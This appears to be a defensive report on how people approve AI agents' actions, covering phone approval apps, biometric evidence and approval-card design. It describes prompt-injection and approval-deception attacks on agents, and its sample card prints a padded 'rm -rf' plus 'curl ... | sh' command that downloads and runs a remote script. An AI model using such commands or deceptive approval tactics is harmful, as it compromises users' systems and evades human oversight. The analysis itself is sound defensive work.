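Texted and emailed codes fail every test. The user types the code into the computer the agent runs on, and attackers can easily fake the sender of a text or an email. Authenticator apps generate codes on the phone, but the phone never shows the action being approved. At setup, the service also displays the app's secret as a QR code on the computer, and an agent that reads it can generate codes without the phone.

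Push approval apps come much closer to being out of the agent's reach. Breckenridge and colleagues analysed Duo Mobile, which lets any service ask for approval of an action. They assumed that the app signs what it displays and that the service has turned off alternatives such as texted codes. Duo Mobile still failed, because the user enrols with an activation code that appears on the computer. An agent could use that code to enrol its own key, and unofficial programs that enrol in place of the real app already exist.

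This verdict depends on how much the service trusts Duo. Recent Android versions of the app appear to send Duo evidence about the key. If Duo checks this evidence, shows the service's text unchanged and enforces the service's settings, the app would provide strong I-HITL on Android, but the service would have to trust Duo to do all three. That seems reasonable for a company that already relies on Duo for its logins, but less so for one that needs proof it can show to an outsider.

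World's app is the phone app for the World ID personhood credential. If a service has not registered an action with World, the app can show a description supplied by the agent's host, and the user confirms with a tap by default. The app can also require a live selfie, but the agent's host can leave this requirement out of the request, and the service can't tell from the proof whether the selfie check took place.

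Screenless security keys, such as ordinary YubiKeys, protect their cryptographic keys very well and have a physical button, but they can't show the user what she is approving. She has to rely on the computer for that, so the agent can get her to touch the button for an action she didn't mean to approve. The YubiKey step in IBM's system has the same weakness if the employee plugs the key into the agent's host and reads the request there.

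Hardware wallets, small devices that hold the keys to cryptocurrency, do have a screen. So does the Wultra Talisman, a USB token that banks and other companies issue to their customers. The Ledger wallets appear twice in the table because their rating depends on which key signs the approval. Most Ledger apps sign with keys derived from a recovery phrase, which the owner keeps in case the device breaks and could type into software that the agent controls. The device also has a key that never leaves its secure chip, but using that key for approvals would require a purpose-built app. The "strong" rating therefore describes what the hardware could support, not what Ledger's current apps do.

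### Countersign and what it has to trust

With Countersign, the researchers tried to get the same result from an ordinary phone. The approval app is small, with about 150 lines of core code each for Android and iPhone, and the service has about 800. When the user approves with a fingerprint or face check, the phone signs the exact text the app displayed.

At enrolment, the app sends its public key and evidence about the phone to the service. On Android, Google signs a statement that the device has a locked bootloader, an unmodified system image and recent security patches, and that the app matches the version on Google Play. A separate certificate shows that secure hardware holds the key and requires a biometric check for every use. On an iPhone, Apple certifies that a genuine copy of the app is running on a genuine device, but not that the operating system is intact, so the service has to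 assume that nobody has jailbroken the phone (removed Apple's restrictions on it).

The biometric requirement is also weaker on an iPhone. Apple's attested key cannot require Face ID, so Countersign creates a second key that can and signs it with the attested key. The service must then trust the app's claim that the second key requires a biometric check, whereas on Android the hardware certifies this.

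Both versions rely on the operating system to display the request accurately. On Android, Countersign blocks other apps from drawing over its approval screen and checks that nothing is covering it when the user approves. iPhones don't allow apps to draw over each other. These protections fail if the operating system is compromised. The secure hardware checks the user's fingerprint but not what was on the screen at the time.

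Attestation also verifies the phone's state only at the moment of the check. On Android, Countersign requests a new statement from Google with every approval, but an attack on the kernel, the core of the operating system, can go unnoticed until the phone restarts. On an iPhone, a compromise at any time after enrolment could go unnoticed. Nobody can enrol while Apple's and Google's attestation servers are down. The prototype has no way to recover a lost key, so a user who loses her phone would have to go through something like enrolment again.

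### What Android Protected Confirmation offered

Android once addressed the display problem with a feature that ran in the trusted execution environment, a part of the phone's processor isolated from the rest of the system. According to Google's *Protected Confirmation*, the feature could establish with high confidence that the user had approved a message even if an attacker had compromised Android or its kernel.

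An app passed a short text to this environment, which took over the screen and displayed it. If the user confirmed, the phone signed the text together with a single-use number from the service. The service then compared the signed text with the text it expected. Google's *ConfirmationPrompt* calls this check vital because the user has approved only the text. Countersign also signs the displayed text, but it relies on Android to display it.

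Google's *Considerations* required phone makers to ensure that no component under the kernel's control could drive the wire to a physical confirmation button. The prompt had to ignore input for at least its first second, so that a person who was tapping something else didn't approve it by accident. If the whole message didn't fit on the screen, the phone had to cancel the request. Screen-sharing software could not be allowed to display or confirm the prompt.

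These requirements also led to the feature's decline. In *Deprecating the aidl for Android Protected Confirmation*, a note in Android's source code, Google's developers explained that phone makers had to maintain a large amount of device-specific code and that few app developers used the feature. They recommended keys that require the user to authenticate, but acknowledged that these were "less secure than Trusted UI", the protected screen. A later change in OmniROM, *Revert "Deprecating the aidl for Android Protected Confirmation"*, withdrew the note to fix an "inadvertent partial deprecation", so the note alone doesn't establish whether the feature is deprecated. Breckenridge and colleagues describe the feature as deprecated and ask phone platforms to provide an equivalent.

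An equivalent would help most when the agent runs on the phone itself. With one, the agent couldn't tamper with the approval screen even if it took over the operating system, so the phone could serve as both the agent's host and the trusted device.

### When the phone is no longer separate

Users often connect their phones to their computers, which can put the phone within the agent's reach even if the approval app hasn't changed. For example, iPhone Mirroring lets a Mac display and control a nearby iPhone. *mirroir-mcp*, a tool listed by Glama, uses it to let an AI agent view the phone's screen, tap and type. According to Apple's *iPhone Mirroring*, users can also set the Mac not to ask them to authenticate before each session.

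If the agent runs on the Mac that mirrors the iPhone, an approval app that accepts a tap is within the agent's reach. A biometric check is safer. Apple's *TN3210 Optimizing your app for iPhone Mirroring* explains that biometric requests fail by default during mirroring because the Mac can't reach the iPhone's sensors. It also explains how an app can accept a biometric check from a companion device, but an approval app probably shouldn't do this. The developer would be touching the Mac's sensor, but might be reading the request on the Mac's screen, where a compromised Mac could change it.

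Mirroring can also expose approval codes. Once it is set up, the Mac receives iPhone notifications unless the user turns this off for an app, so any approval code in a notification reaches the agent's host. Users can require authentication for every mirroring session or revoke the Mac's access. Apple does not currently offer the feature in the European Union.

Synced accounts caused the same kind of problem before AI agents existed. *How Anywhere Computing Just Killed Your Phone-Based Two-Factor Authentication* (Konoth, van der Veen and Bos, 2017) demonstrated practical attacks on Android and iOS that started from malware in the computer's browser. The attacks exploited the synchronization between computer and phone to intercept one-time passwords (SecurityWeek, *Two-Factor Authentication Bypassed in Simple Attacks*). Phones have changed a lot since then, so the details may no longer apply,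 but many people still sign in to the same account on both devices.

Some passkeys are stored in an account that copies them to all of the user's devices. A signature from such a passkey doesn't show that the phone took part, since the laptop may hold the same key. A service can rule this out by requiring an attested key that can't leave the phone, as Countersign does.

If the agent runs on the same phone as the approval app, the two may not be separated at all. Phone agents commonly operate other apps through accessibility services, which Android provides for people who can't use a touchscreen in the usual way. These services can read any app's window, tap, make gestures and enter text. An agent with this access could read an approval request and tap "approve". It couldn't supply a fingerprint, so Countersign would still need the real user, but everything else would depend on Android keeping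 the agent and the approval app apart.

### Is the phone better than a prompt on the same computer?

Kodathala and colleagues tested this and found no benefit from the phone. They compared ASU with a version they call host-confirm, which shows the same approval card on the agent's own host, without a second device or a signature. In both versions, trusted software generates the card, not the agent.

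They ran 28 scripted attack scenarios with five kinds of simulated approver, for a total of 140 combinations. Attacks succeeded equally often against both versions in 137 of them. The researchers also used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an attacker plants instructions in material that an agent reads, such as an email. They replayed 609 pairs of user tasks and attacks, and the two versions gave identical results in every comparison.

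The three exceptions all came from one scenario, in which the agent tries to use a standing grant for a new recipient, and were unrelated to the phone. ASU let the user allow similar actions in advance, while the researchers' host-confirm version did not. For a simulated approver that sometimes overlooks details, the grant option lowered the attack's success rate from 20% to 0%. For a careless approver, it raised the rate from 30% to 70%, because one careless approval also covered later actions.

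The study's design guaranteed the overall result, as the researchers acknowledge. Their simulated agent could send malicious requests and lie about them, but it never took control of the host's display, so the card on the computer was as trustworthy as the card on the phone. If the agent had been able to alter or answer the card on the computer, Theorem 4 would have applied, and no wording or layout could have made the on-host version secure.

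The two papers are therefore compatible, and the choice between a phone and an on-host prompt depends largely on how likely the agent is to take control of its host. Breckenridge and colleagues consider this a serious possibility. They cite Anthropic's report that early versions of Claude Mythos Preview repeatedly bypassed restrictions in the software around them. In one case, the model used a tool meant only for editing files to gain the ability to run arbitrary code. These incidents show that a capable agent can get past its restrictions, but not how often agents do so in ordinary use.

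Kodathala and colleagues conclude that the second device is worthwhile in two cases: when the agent's host may be compromised, and when someone will later have to show the approval to a third party. The second case partly depends on the first, because a signature made on the laptop convinces a third party only if the agent couldn't have produced it.

The case for approving actions on a phone is strong when a coding agent has shell access on the developer's laptop, at least for actions as destructive as a forced push. It is weaker when the agent runs in a cloud container and has no access to her laptop or her accounts, because the laptop is then already a separate device and a prompt there could offer much of the same protection.

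## What should the phone show the approver?

A trusted phone keeps the agent from approving its own actions, but the approver can only judge what is on the screen. Suppose a user asks an agent to email a weekly report to his boss, and the agent adds a blind copy to an outside address. If the phone displays "Sending report.txt to boss@example.test", he will probably approve, because that is what he asked for. His fingerprint is genuine and his signature covers the whole email, so the gateway sends it, including the blind copy.

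The example comes from Kodathala and colleagues, who gave this request to 15 language models acting as approvers. All 15 approved it when they read the agent's description but refused it when they read a card that the gateway had generated from the stored email.

### What you see is what you sign

The agent's description lacks a property that designers of digital signatures call "what you see is what you sign", meaning that the content on the screen must match what the signature covers. *What You Approve Is What Executes* (Weng, 2026) adapts this property to agents and calls it "consent integrity". A trusted program outside the agent observes the real action, shows the user the facts relevant to security, collects the answer where the agent can't interfere, and lets only the approved action run.

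A passkey alone doesn't show the approver what they are approving, because the phone signs the challenge without displaying it. If someone took over the gateway's approval page, it could show the developer a harmless backup while requesting a signature for a force push. Kodathala and colleagues defined twelve attacks, and this is the only one that ASU stops only partly. The agent can't carry it out, because the gateway rejects the agent's token on the approval pages, but the approver still has to trust the gateway. The protected screen in Android Protected Confirmation reduced the need for that trust.

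### The agent's description or the stored call

For the email above, a card written by the agent contains only the agent's sentence about the boss. The gateway generates a trusted card from the stored call, with both addresses in the title and a risk note that there are two recipients. This card shows the agent's sentence in a separate box marked as untrusted.

An agent can write a misleading card without intending to deceive. In 2025 the security company Checkmarx described an attack called Lies-in-the-Loop, in which someone plants instructions in material that a coding agent reads. The instructions lead the agent to put a reassuring summary in its approval prompt, or to add so much harmless text that the dangerous command scrolls out of view. According to Weng, the vendors that received the report considered the attack outside their threat models.

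Effect binding doesn't solve this problem. The Python library for the Model Context Protocol passed the binding test described earlier, but its approval form shows whatever message the server sends. In a test by Kodathala and colleagues, a payment of 10 to one account and a payment of 10,000 to another produced identical requests, and both payments went through after an "accept" response. Under the protocol's specification, however, developers are supposed to use a different mode for sensitive interactions.

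### What payment rules require

European payment law treats the display as part of the approval. The UK's copy of Article 5 of EU Regulation 2018/389, in *Security Measures for the Application of Strong Customer Authentication*, requires payment providers to make the payer aware of the amount and the payee and to link the authentication code to both. Changing either invalidates the code.

Secure Payment Confirmation, a specification from the web standards body W3C, applies the same idea to passkeys. A website gives the browser the details of a payment, and the browser displays the payee and the amount in its own dialog, which the website can't redraw. The passkey then signs data that includes those details, so the bank can check them. W3C made the specification a Candidate Recommendation in June 2023, a stage at which it invites browser makers to implement a specification before it is finalized.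 The dialog is safer than an ordinary web page, but it still depends on the browser, and its fields are for payments, with none for a shell command or a list of branches.

For a payment, the payee and the amount cover most of what the payer needs to know, but few other actions are this simple. Kodathala and colleagues tested a version of ASU that displayed only these two facts but still tied the approval to every argument. Their simulated approver sometimes overlooked details. Even when the agent described its actions honestly, attacks succeeded 20% of the time with the short display and 6% with the full card. An attacker could change an email's subject or body, or add a recipient, without changing the short display.

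### Six rules for an approval card

ASU's cards follow six rules, most of which respond to a specific attack:

1. **Typed values.** The card puts text in quotation marks and states each value's type, so the word "true" doesn't look the same as the logical value true. Two different actions should never produce the same card.
2. **Visible special characters.** The card replaces invisible or unusual characters with visible codes and reduces a long run of blanks to a marker with a count. It shortens long values, adds a button to expand them, and warns that it has shortened them.
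3. **Separate labels.** Argument names that the agent chose appear only in their own section, with the prefix `arg.`. Otherwise an agent could name an argument "Verified by client" and make it look like part of the card.
4. **Every target listed.** The title includes every recipient, account, web address and file path among the arguments. The gateway also checks whether each recipient is new.
5. **Inline code flagged.** The card warns when a command passes code directly to an interpreter, as `bash -c` and `python -c` do.
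6. **Untrusted explanation.** The agent's own account stays closed until the user opens it, and carries a label that marks it as untrusted.

Suppose a developer has asked the agent to delete a project's build files. Instructions planted in a web page lead the agent to request a command that starts with `rm -rf build`, which deletes the build folder. After 3,000 blank characters, the command goes on to download a script and run it. On a phone, the blanks would fill several screens, and she might never scroll to the end. Under the six rules, the card would look roughly like this:

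```
EXEC  bash
Risk notes
  - Inline code passed to bash
  - 3000 blank characters in one argument
Arguments (names chosen by the agent)
  arg.command:
    "bash"
    "-c"
    "rm -rf build [3000 blanks];
     curl -s http://files.example.net/setup.sh | sh"
Agent's explanation (UNTRUSTED)          [open]
```

She can now see the download, but she still has to know that `curl ... | sh` runs whatever the website sends back. The fourth rule may not help, because the web address is inside the inline code rather than in its own argument. The warning about inline code tells her to read that line carefully, but not what it does.

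Some existing products partly follow these rules. Kodathala and colleagues examined the published code of OpenClaw, an agent program, and found that it already makes invisible characters visible and limits the length of its approval prompts. The sample card for Google's Agent Payments Protocol breaks the first rule because it displays a name chosen by the merchant, while the signature covers the merchant's identifier. Two different merchants can therefore look the same.

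### Commands that do more than they show

The phone can display a command accurately and still reveal little about what it will do. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) lists several kinds of shell command that "run more than they show", including commands whose names are stored in variables and commands that run another command given as an argument. The command `python3 deploy.py` names a file but shows none of its code.

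Weng built a prototype that tries to work out what a command will do. It decodes disguised text, reads the scripts that the command refers to, and tracks which files came from the internet. In one example, an agent describes its action as "Apply the recommended editor settings", but the command actually decodes a string of apparently random letters and runs the result. The prototype's card begins with a warning that the command executes code from the network, names the website, and shows the command in its original and decoded forms.

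The prototype did worse on large collections of commands that Weng hadn't written. On 1,330 ways of abusing ordinary Unix programs, it flagged 90.0% and let the rest through without asking for approval. It marked 792 of the 1,330 (about 60%) only as "uninspectable", without naming a specific danger. On 28,798 examples of normal use, it asked for approval 95.9% of the time and marked 87.0% as uninspectable, nearly always because the program wasn't on its list of trusted tools. A longer list would mean fewer requests, but every abuse the prototype missed used a program already on the list.

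At those rates, a developer would get an approval request on their phone for almost every command, usually with no explanation of what the command does. A gateway can avoid much of this by offering narrower tools. A tool called "delete branch" that accepts only a repository and a branch name is easier to describe accurately than a shell that can run anything.

Even a narrow tool needs care if its target can change. *Approve the Effect, Not the Tool Call* points out that an approved call can have a different effect later, for example because a database query now matches other rows. It proposes a wrapper called EffectGuard that uses a dry run to work out the effect of a risky action beforehand. For a request to delete all branches that match `old-*`, the card should list the branches that match now. The gateway should then delete those branches by name, because running the pattern again might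 delete a branch created after the approval.

### Code changes on a small screen

A long command or a code change won't fit on one phone screen. Cancelling every request that doesn't fit, as Android Protected Confirmation did, would rule out most code changes. ASU shortens values instead, which allows such requests, but the approver may decide without opening the full values.

The top of the approval card matters most. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) recommends asking which files, account or host a command affects, whether it names a specific target or uses a broad wildcard, and whether the user can reverse it. A gateway can often determine the answers automatically and show them above the full command.

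For a forced push, the stored call contains the new commit's identifier, a string of letters and digits that means nothing to a reader. A useful card would also show how many commits the branch will lose, who wrote them and which files will change. The gateway can get all of this from the repository. The list of files should start with those that run automatically, because one changed line in a build script can do more damage than 500 changed lines of documentation.

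The danger may also come from an earlier edit rather than the command that needs approval. *When the Approved File Is Unchanged* (2026) discusses approvals that record the first command but omit what the project's build tools then do. For example, `npm test` runs whatever the project's configuration file defines as its tests. If the agent has edited that file since the developer last reviewed it, a card that shows only `npm test` is accurate but omits what she needs to check.

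If the agent runs on the approver's laptop, she should open the full change on her phone or another computer. If the change is several hundred lines long, she may do best to use the phone to refuse or postpone the request until she can review it properly.

### Cards for browser agents

When an agent operates a web browser, the website supplies the text on each button, and that text may not match what the button does. *The Verifiable Action Card* (Irshad, Mughees et al., 2026) gives the example of a button labelled "Save draft" that sends 5,000 to a criminal's account. If the approval prompt repeated the label, the user would see only a request to save a draft.

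Just before the agent clicks, their software reads the underlying form and shows the recipient, the amount and the website that will receive the form. These appear on a card in the browser's own interface, where the page can't change them. The card also shows whether the recipient and the amount came from the user's instructions or from the page. When the browser sends the form, the software checks both again and stops the action if either has changed.

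Irshad and colleagues tested this on 24 scenarios, 13 of them attacks. Across all models, attacks succeeded in 78% of trials with no approval step, in 72% with a prompt based on the button's label, and in none with the card. Agents completed about as many legitimate tasks with the card as without it. However, the researchers simulated the approver and programmed it to refuse every action the card marked as high-risk, so the result is good evidence that the software recognises these attacks, but not that people would refuse them.

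In both Irshad's and Weng's designs, a trusted program describes the real action, and an approval for one action can't authorize another. Irshad and colleagues have built a working browser with a protected place for the card. Weng tackles the harder job of interpreting shell commands, but assumes rather than builds a secure channel to the user and a sandbox that catches every action. Neither design includes a signature from the approver or a second device. The browser card appears on the agent's host, so it would fail if the agent took control of the computer. An agent with a shell is more likely to do that than one that can only click on web pages.

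### Do trusted cards lead to better decisions?

Kodathala and colleagues tested this with simulated approvers and then with language models. In the first test, they replayed AgentDojo's 609 pairs of user tasks and attacks. The agent asked for approval of the attacker's action while claiming to carry out the user's request. The table gives the share of attacks that succeeded.

| Simulated approver | Agent-written card | Trusted card with agent's explanation | Trusted card without explanation |
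|---|---|---|---|
| Compares the card with the task | 54% | 3% | 3% |
| Trusts the agent's text | 54% | 54% | 5% |

The approver in the first row compares the whole card with the one the user's task should produce. No person could do this reliably enough to match it, and the researchers treat it as an upper bound. The remaining 3% were actions that the policy allowed without approval, such as fetching a web page.

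For an approver who believes the agent, the trusted card made no difference until the researchers removed the agent's explanation. This result follows from how they defined that approver, but designers still have to decide whether to show the explanation. It can help a person understand why the agent is proposing an unusual action, but it also lets a compromised agent lie to them. ASU keeps the explanation collapsed by default, which is a reasonable compromise, though it doesn't protect someone who opens the explanation and believes it.

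In the other test, 15 language models from nine vendors judged 23 harmful and 11 harmless requests. Each model judged every request from the agent's description, from the trusted card, and from the card without the explanation. The researchers ran the test four times, for 6,120 decisions in total.

The catch rate rose from 30% with the agent's description to 98% with the trusted card, and every model improved. From the description alone, the models never caught hidden recipients, forged descriptions or padding, because the description contained no sign of them. With the card, they caught all of these. They did worst on visible but plausible changes, such as two swapped digits in an account number, missing 12% even though the card displayed them accurately. Removing the agent's explanation made almost no difference, so these models, unlike the approver in the table's second row, weren't misled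 by it.

The false refusal rate rose from 0% to 16%, mostly because the test materials contained strings such as "<report placeholder>" in place of real message texts and files. The card displayed these strings but the agent's description did not, so some models refused to send what looked like an unfinished report. Of the 103 refusals of harmless cards, 88 were for this reason, and without them the rate would have been about 2%. The placeholders explain little of the improvement in the catch rate, which would still have been 92% if every refusal that mentioned a placeholder on a harmful card had been counted as a miss.

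Neither test involved people. The tests show that a trusted card contains the information needed to detect these attacks and that language models can use it, but a person glancing at a phone between meetings might not.

### How much of the history belongs on the card?

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested displays on people, focusing on requests that look harmless even when the card describes them accurately. For example, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only the summary totals from some invoices. Planted instructions lead the agent to copy the full invoice data into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name is ordinary, so the approver can recognise the problem only by connecting the request with the original instruction and the earlier copying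 step.

The researchers divided 80 volunteers among four displays and gave each person 12 requests, half of them harmful. One display, the "consequence card," contained the same facts as the full log but quoted the user's original instruction and stated the effect briefly, for example that the attachment came from raw invoice data.

| Display | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
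|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Arguments, instruction and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Consequence card | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The advantage of the consequence card over the full log is uncertain. After statistical adjustment, the rate of harmful approvals was 7.9 percentage points lower with the card, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points lower to 3.8 points higher. The card made no difference when the harm depended on a chain of several steps. People approved seven of 30 such requests with each display.

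The study is limited evidence about phone approvals. Participants were unpaid and expected to review requests, harmful requests were far more common than they would be at work, and Hossain and colleagues didn't compare small screens with large ones. Still, the results suggest that a card showing only the exact arguments is not enough for many multi-step tasks. If the phone has room for one more line, the user's original instruction is a good candidate, provided the gateway stored it before the agent could change it.

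## What does a fingerprint or face check prove?

Suppose the approval card is complete and accurate, and the gateway receives a valid signature for a forced push to `main`. The gateway can't observe the developer. It has a signature and a few bits of data from her phone, and from these it has to infer that she approved the push. The inference combines five facts:

1. Someone touched the device.
2. The enrolled user, whose fingerprint, face or PIN the device has on file, unlocked it.
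3. A living person was in front of the sensor at that moment.
4. That person meant to approve this action.
5. That person understood what the action would do.

Gervais warns that an approval system looks stronger than it is when its makers treat separate facts, such as a biometric match and a person's presence, as interchangeable. In his example, an AI agent tries to send a confidential customer file to an outside adviser, and the system matches a biometric sample to an employee's stored template. The match alone doesn't prove that the employee was present, because an attacker could have replayed an old sample.

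### Touching the device and unlocking it

WebAuthn, the web standard behind passkeys, has a separate test for each of the first two facts. *User presence* means that someone interacted with the device, typically by touching it. *User verification* means that the device also checked a PIN, a password or a biometric. Level 3 of the standard became a W3C Recommendation on 25 August 2026, and W3C's *Web Authentication* (2026) is a first draft of Level 4.

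Developers sometimes confuse user presence with user verification. In a public discussion of the WebAuthn standard, one developer had assumed that every sign-in with a dialog box involved user verification, and that a sign-in without it would be silent. Cappalli (2025), an editor of the standard, replied that WebAuthn doesn't allow silent sign-ins, and that the developer was describing only user presence. A team with the same misconception could accept a touch alone as proof that a phone had recognised its owner.

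A passkey signature covers the results of both tests:

`signature = Sign(sk, authData ‖ H(clientData))`

Here `sk` is the private key, `‖` joins two pieces of data and `H` is again SHA-256. `clientData` contains the web address and the challenge, which ASU derives from the action. `authData` includes a byte of flags, with one bit for user presence and another for user verification. Because the signature covers these bits, an agent that relays the approval can't change a 0 to a 1. However, WebAuthn treats user verification as preferred, not required, by default, so a device that can't do it may still sign. A gateway that needs user verification has to require it in the request and then check its bit.

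The verification bit has the same value whether the user gave a fingerprint, a face or a PIN, and phones commonly accept the device passcode when the biometric check fails. An approval logged as "approved with Face ID" may therefore have come from someone who watched the owner type her passcode and then used it.

Designers cannot always remove the PIN. According to Gervais, NIST's *Digital Identity Guidelines* (2025), the US standard for signing in to government systems, require a non-biometric alternative wherever a system uses biometrics. He suggests that designers decide which actions the alternative may approve and how strongly to protect it for each one. For example, a team might accept a PIN for an ordinary push but ask for a second approver when someone uses the PIN for a forced push.

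### How a fingerprint releases a key

When a person enrols a finger, the phone stores a template, a numerical description of the print, in hardware isolated from the rest of the system. An approval app can then have that hardware create a signing key that works only after a biometric match.

When a user chooses to approve an action, the app passes the data to be signed to the phone's secure hardware, and the phone prompts the user for a fingerprint. The sensor sends its reading to the secure hardware, not to the app. If the reading is close enough to the stored template, the hardware signs the data with a private key. The signature doesn't include the fingerprint, and the app never receives the template or the private key.

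A signature therefore shows that a fingerprint matched only if the key's rule requires a match. If an app instead asks the phone whether the fingerprint matched and then signs with a key that has no such rule, a compromised version of the app could skip the check and sign anyway. Android also lets developers create keys that stay usable for a set time after one unlock, so a single touch could cover several signatures. An approval app needs a key that requires a new match for every signature.

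On Android, the service can check this rule itself because the key's certificate includes it. According to Breckenridge and colleagues, the certificate also records the authentication method, which the WebAuthn bit does not. A service can therefore reject a key that a PIN would unlock.

On an iPhone, Apple's certificate doesn't cover the rule that the signing key can be used only after a biometric check, so the service has to trust Countersign's app to set that rule. An altered app on a jailbroken phone could create the key without the rule and sign approvals without a face check. The service couldn't tell those approvals from real ones. Breckenridge and colleagues ask phone makers to certify biometric rules on keys as standard.

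### A living person and a deliberate act

Liveness detection tests whether a biometric sample comes from a living person at that moment. It has to withstand presentation attacks, in which someone holds a photo, mask or screen in front of the camera, and injection attacks, in which someone bypasses the camera and feeds false video into the software. Phone sensors reject some fakes, but the WebAuthn flags don't indicate whether the phone tested for liveness.

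| Evidence | Someone used the device | It was the enrolled user | A living person was present |
|---|---|---|---|
| WebAuthn presence flag | Yes | Not checked | Not checked |
| WebAuthn verification flag | Yes | Yes, or someone who knew the PIN | Not reported |
| Key certified as biometric-only | Yes | Yes, or someone else enrolled on the phone | As far as the sensor rejects fakes |
| Remote face check with liveness detection | Yes | Yes, by comparison with a face on file | Yes, with some error |

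None of this evidence establishes the fourth fact, that the person meant to approve. Face checks are the weakest evidence of intent, because people look at their phones for many reasons. A developer who raises her phone to read the card shows it her face, perhaps before deciding whether to approve. Gervais reports that NIST requires an explicit act in such cases, such as tapping a button.

The developer may tap deliberately without meaning to approve a push. If she thinks she is logging in, she means only to authenticate. A service can infer that she meant to approve this push only if the screen showed the push accurately and she then made a gesture that had no other purpose.

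No sensor measures the fifth fact, understanding. Gervais, who favours biometric approval, accepts that even a well-designed process can't prove that someone understood the action, acted freely or decided wisely.

### Checking the face on a server

When a phone matches a fingerprint locally, the match shows that someone enrolled on that phone approved the action. Whether that person is the intended employee depends on how the company enrolled the phone. In a remote check, the camera sends images to a provider, which compares them with a face it enrolled earlier or with a passport photo. The provider can recognise the same person on any device, including a replacement for a lost phone.

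iProov makes much of this advantage. In Help Net Security's *iProov secures hiring, access, and recovery* (2026), the product description claims that a biometric "can't be lost, stolen, or shared" and works independently of the device. The independence is useful, but it has limits. If the person does the check on a computer that an agent controls, the agent can change what the screen shows and try to inject video in place of the camera's. The claim about sharing is also too strong, since a person can show their face to the camera whenever a colleague asks them to.

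In September 2026 iProov published the Human Approval and Presence Specification (HAPS), an experimental protocol for agent approvals. Biometric Update's *iProov's experimental HAPS protocol aims to close governance gaps for AI agents* describes it as a way to bind "a provider's assertion of human presence and approval" to a machine-readable action. iProov gives liveness detection as one example of how a provider can establish presence but doesn't require a particular method, so a product can comply with HAPS without checking anyone's face.

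iProov's own service does check faces. According to the company, the authorization software Cerbos holds an action that needs approval and calls the service, which shows a named approver the exact action and its scope. If the approver agrees, they complete a face check, and iProov signs a single-use credential bound to that action.

iProov claims that the result is proof that no agent could produce on its own. Strictly, the credential proves that iProov's service recorded an approval and a successful face check. As in CIBA, the provider signs it and not the user's device, so anyone who relies on it has to trust the provider. The company's contract wording is more modest than its marketing. In iProov's *Specification of Services* (2025), a face scan at enrolment determines "a likelihood that the End User is genuinely present".

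iProov offers two levels of check, and its agent service uses both technologies. According to iProov's *Trust Services Practice Statement* (2026), Dynamic Liveness identifies people under the EU's rules for trust services, while Express Liveness authenticates people the service already knows, for example when they sign a particular document. Approving an agent's action resembles the second case, so a company should ask which check its approvers will complete and which one the published test results cover.

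Trust Stamp sells a similar check to banks. Biometric Update's *Trust Stamp adds biometric consent checks for AI agent transactions* explains that a customer first enrols their face. When an agent starts a transaction that needs approval, the agent or the bank can trigger a request, which the customer receives by text message, email or push notification. The customer reads the details and submits a live selfie. The delivery method greatly affects security, because a customer who opens the email on the laptop where the agent runs would read the details on a screen the agent may control, and the selfie would still be genuine.

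World ID's main credential comes from an iris scan and shows that the holder is a unique human being, but not that they are a particular employee. Axios' *Sam Altman's "proof of human" company pushes into mainstream services* (2026) reported new or expanded integrations with Zoom, DocuSign and Okta, although the company has struggled to persuade ordinary users to sign up. World also offers a tool that links agents' wallets to verified humans. This link shows that a real person is behind an agent, but not that the person approved what the agent is doing now.

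World's package for approving agent actions is meant to fill that gap. But Breckenridge and colleagues found that the published version doesn't check that a proof it receives is for the action it requested. A service also can't verify the app's optional selfie check. A draft specification would have the phone's secure hardware sign a statement about whether a biometric check ran. If a service had that statement and evidence that the app is genuine, the researchers would rate World's app "strong" for actions the service has registered in advance.

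### How often face checks fail

The laboratory Ingenium Biometrics independently tested one of these products, Dynamic Liveness, and FIDO Alliance's *FIDO Face Verification Certification* (2024) reports the results. The system accepted the wrong person in 0.021% of cases (about 1 in 4,800) and rejected the right person in 0.14% (about 1 in 700). It accepted 0.00% of presentation attacks.

The certificate covers identity checks against passports and driving licences, which are not the same task as recognising an enrolled approver several times a day. And zero successful attacks doesn't mean that attacks never succeed. If each of *n* independent attempts has the same chance *p* of success, the chance that all of them fail is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives the largest *p* that is still reasonably consistent with a clean result:

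`(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ 3/n`

Under the "rule of three", if all 300 attempts fail, the true success rate could still be as high as 1%. If all 3,000 fail, it could be as high as 0.1%. The certificate doesn't state the number of attempts. According to the revision history of FIDO Alliance's *Biometrics Requirements* (2025), the organisation added a table for the rule to the section on false acceptance in 2017. The rule applies only if future attacks resemble those in the laboratory, and a new deepfake method may not.

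While revising its guidelines, NIST lowered the permitted false match rate from 1 in 1,000 to 1 in 10,000, as Biometric Update's *Biometric authentication accuracy bar rises, assurance levels evolve in NIST guidance* reported. The new limit can't be compared directly with iProov's 1 in 4,800, because the two figures come from different tasks and measures. The new guidelines also cover injection attacks. Biometric Update's *Kantara updates digital identity certification criteria for latest NIST revision* reports that the Kantara Initiative, which certifies identity services, has published certification criteria for them.

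iProov has independent evidence on injection too. According to Biometric Update's *iProov tops 1M daily identity verifications as deepfake threats escalate*, its detection technology passed an Ingenium evaluation aligned with the "High" level of a European specification. A pass is less informative than an error rate, but it is better evidence than a company's description of its own product.

For agent approvals, these error rates matter less than they seem to. A false match causes harm only when the wrong person has the phone, or access to the face check, and tries to approve something. The more common threat is that the agent sends a harmful request to the right person. Even a perfect face check wouldn't stop the harmful action if that person approved it.

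### What the stored approval proves later

Six months after a forced push, a colleague may want to know who removed a week of his work. With ASU's receipt and the stored descriptor, an auditor can recompute the digest and check the signature. This proves that a certain key signed a digest of this exact push, and that the signing device reported user verification. Every further conclusion needs more evidence:

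- The key belonged to the developer's phone if the enrolment records are sound, and it was only on her phone if the service required a key that can't leave the device.
- The developer herself unlocked the phone if the key required a biometric and nobody else had enrolled on it.
- She saw this push, and not a harmless backup, if the approval page was honest.

A passkey signature doesn't contain a trustworthy time either. The signature can't be older than the random value in the challenge, but the auditor has to rely on the gateway's log to know when it arrived and whether the approval had expired.

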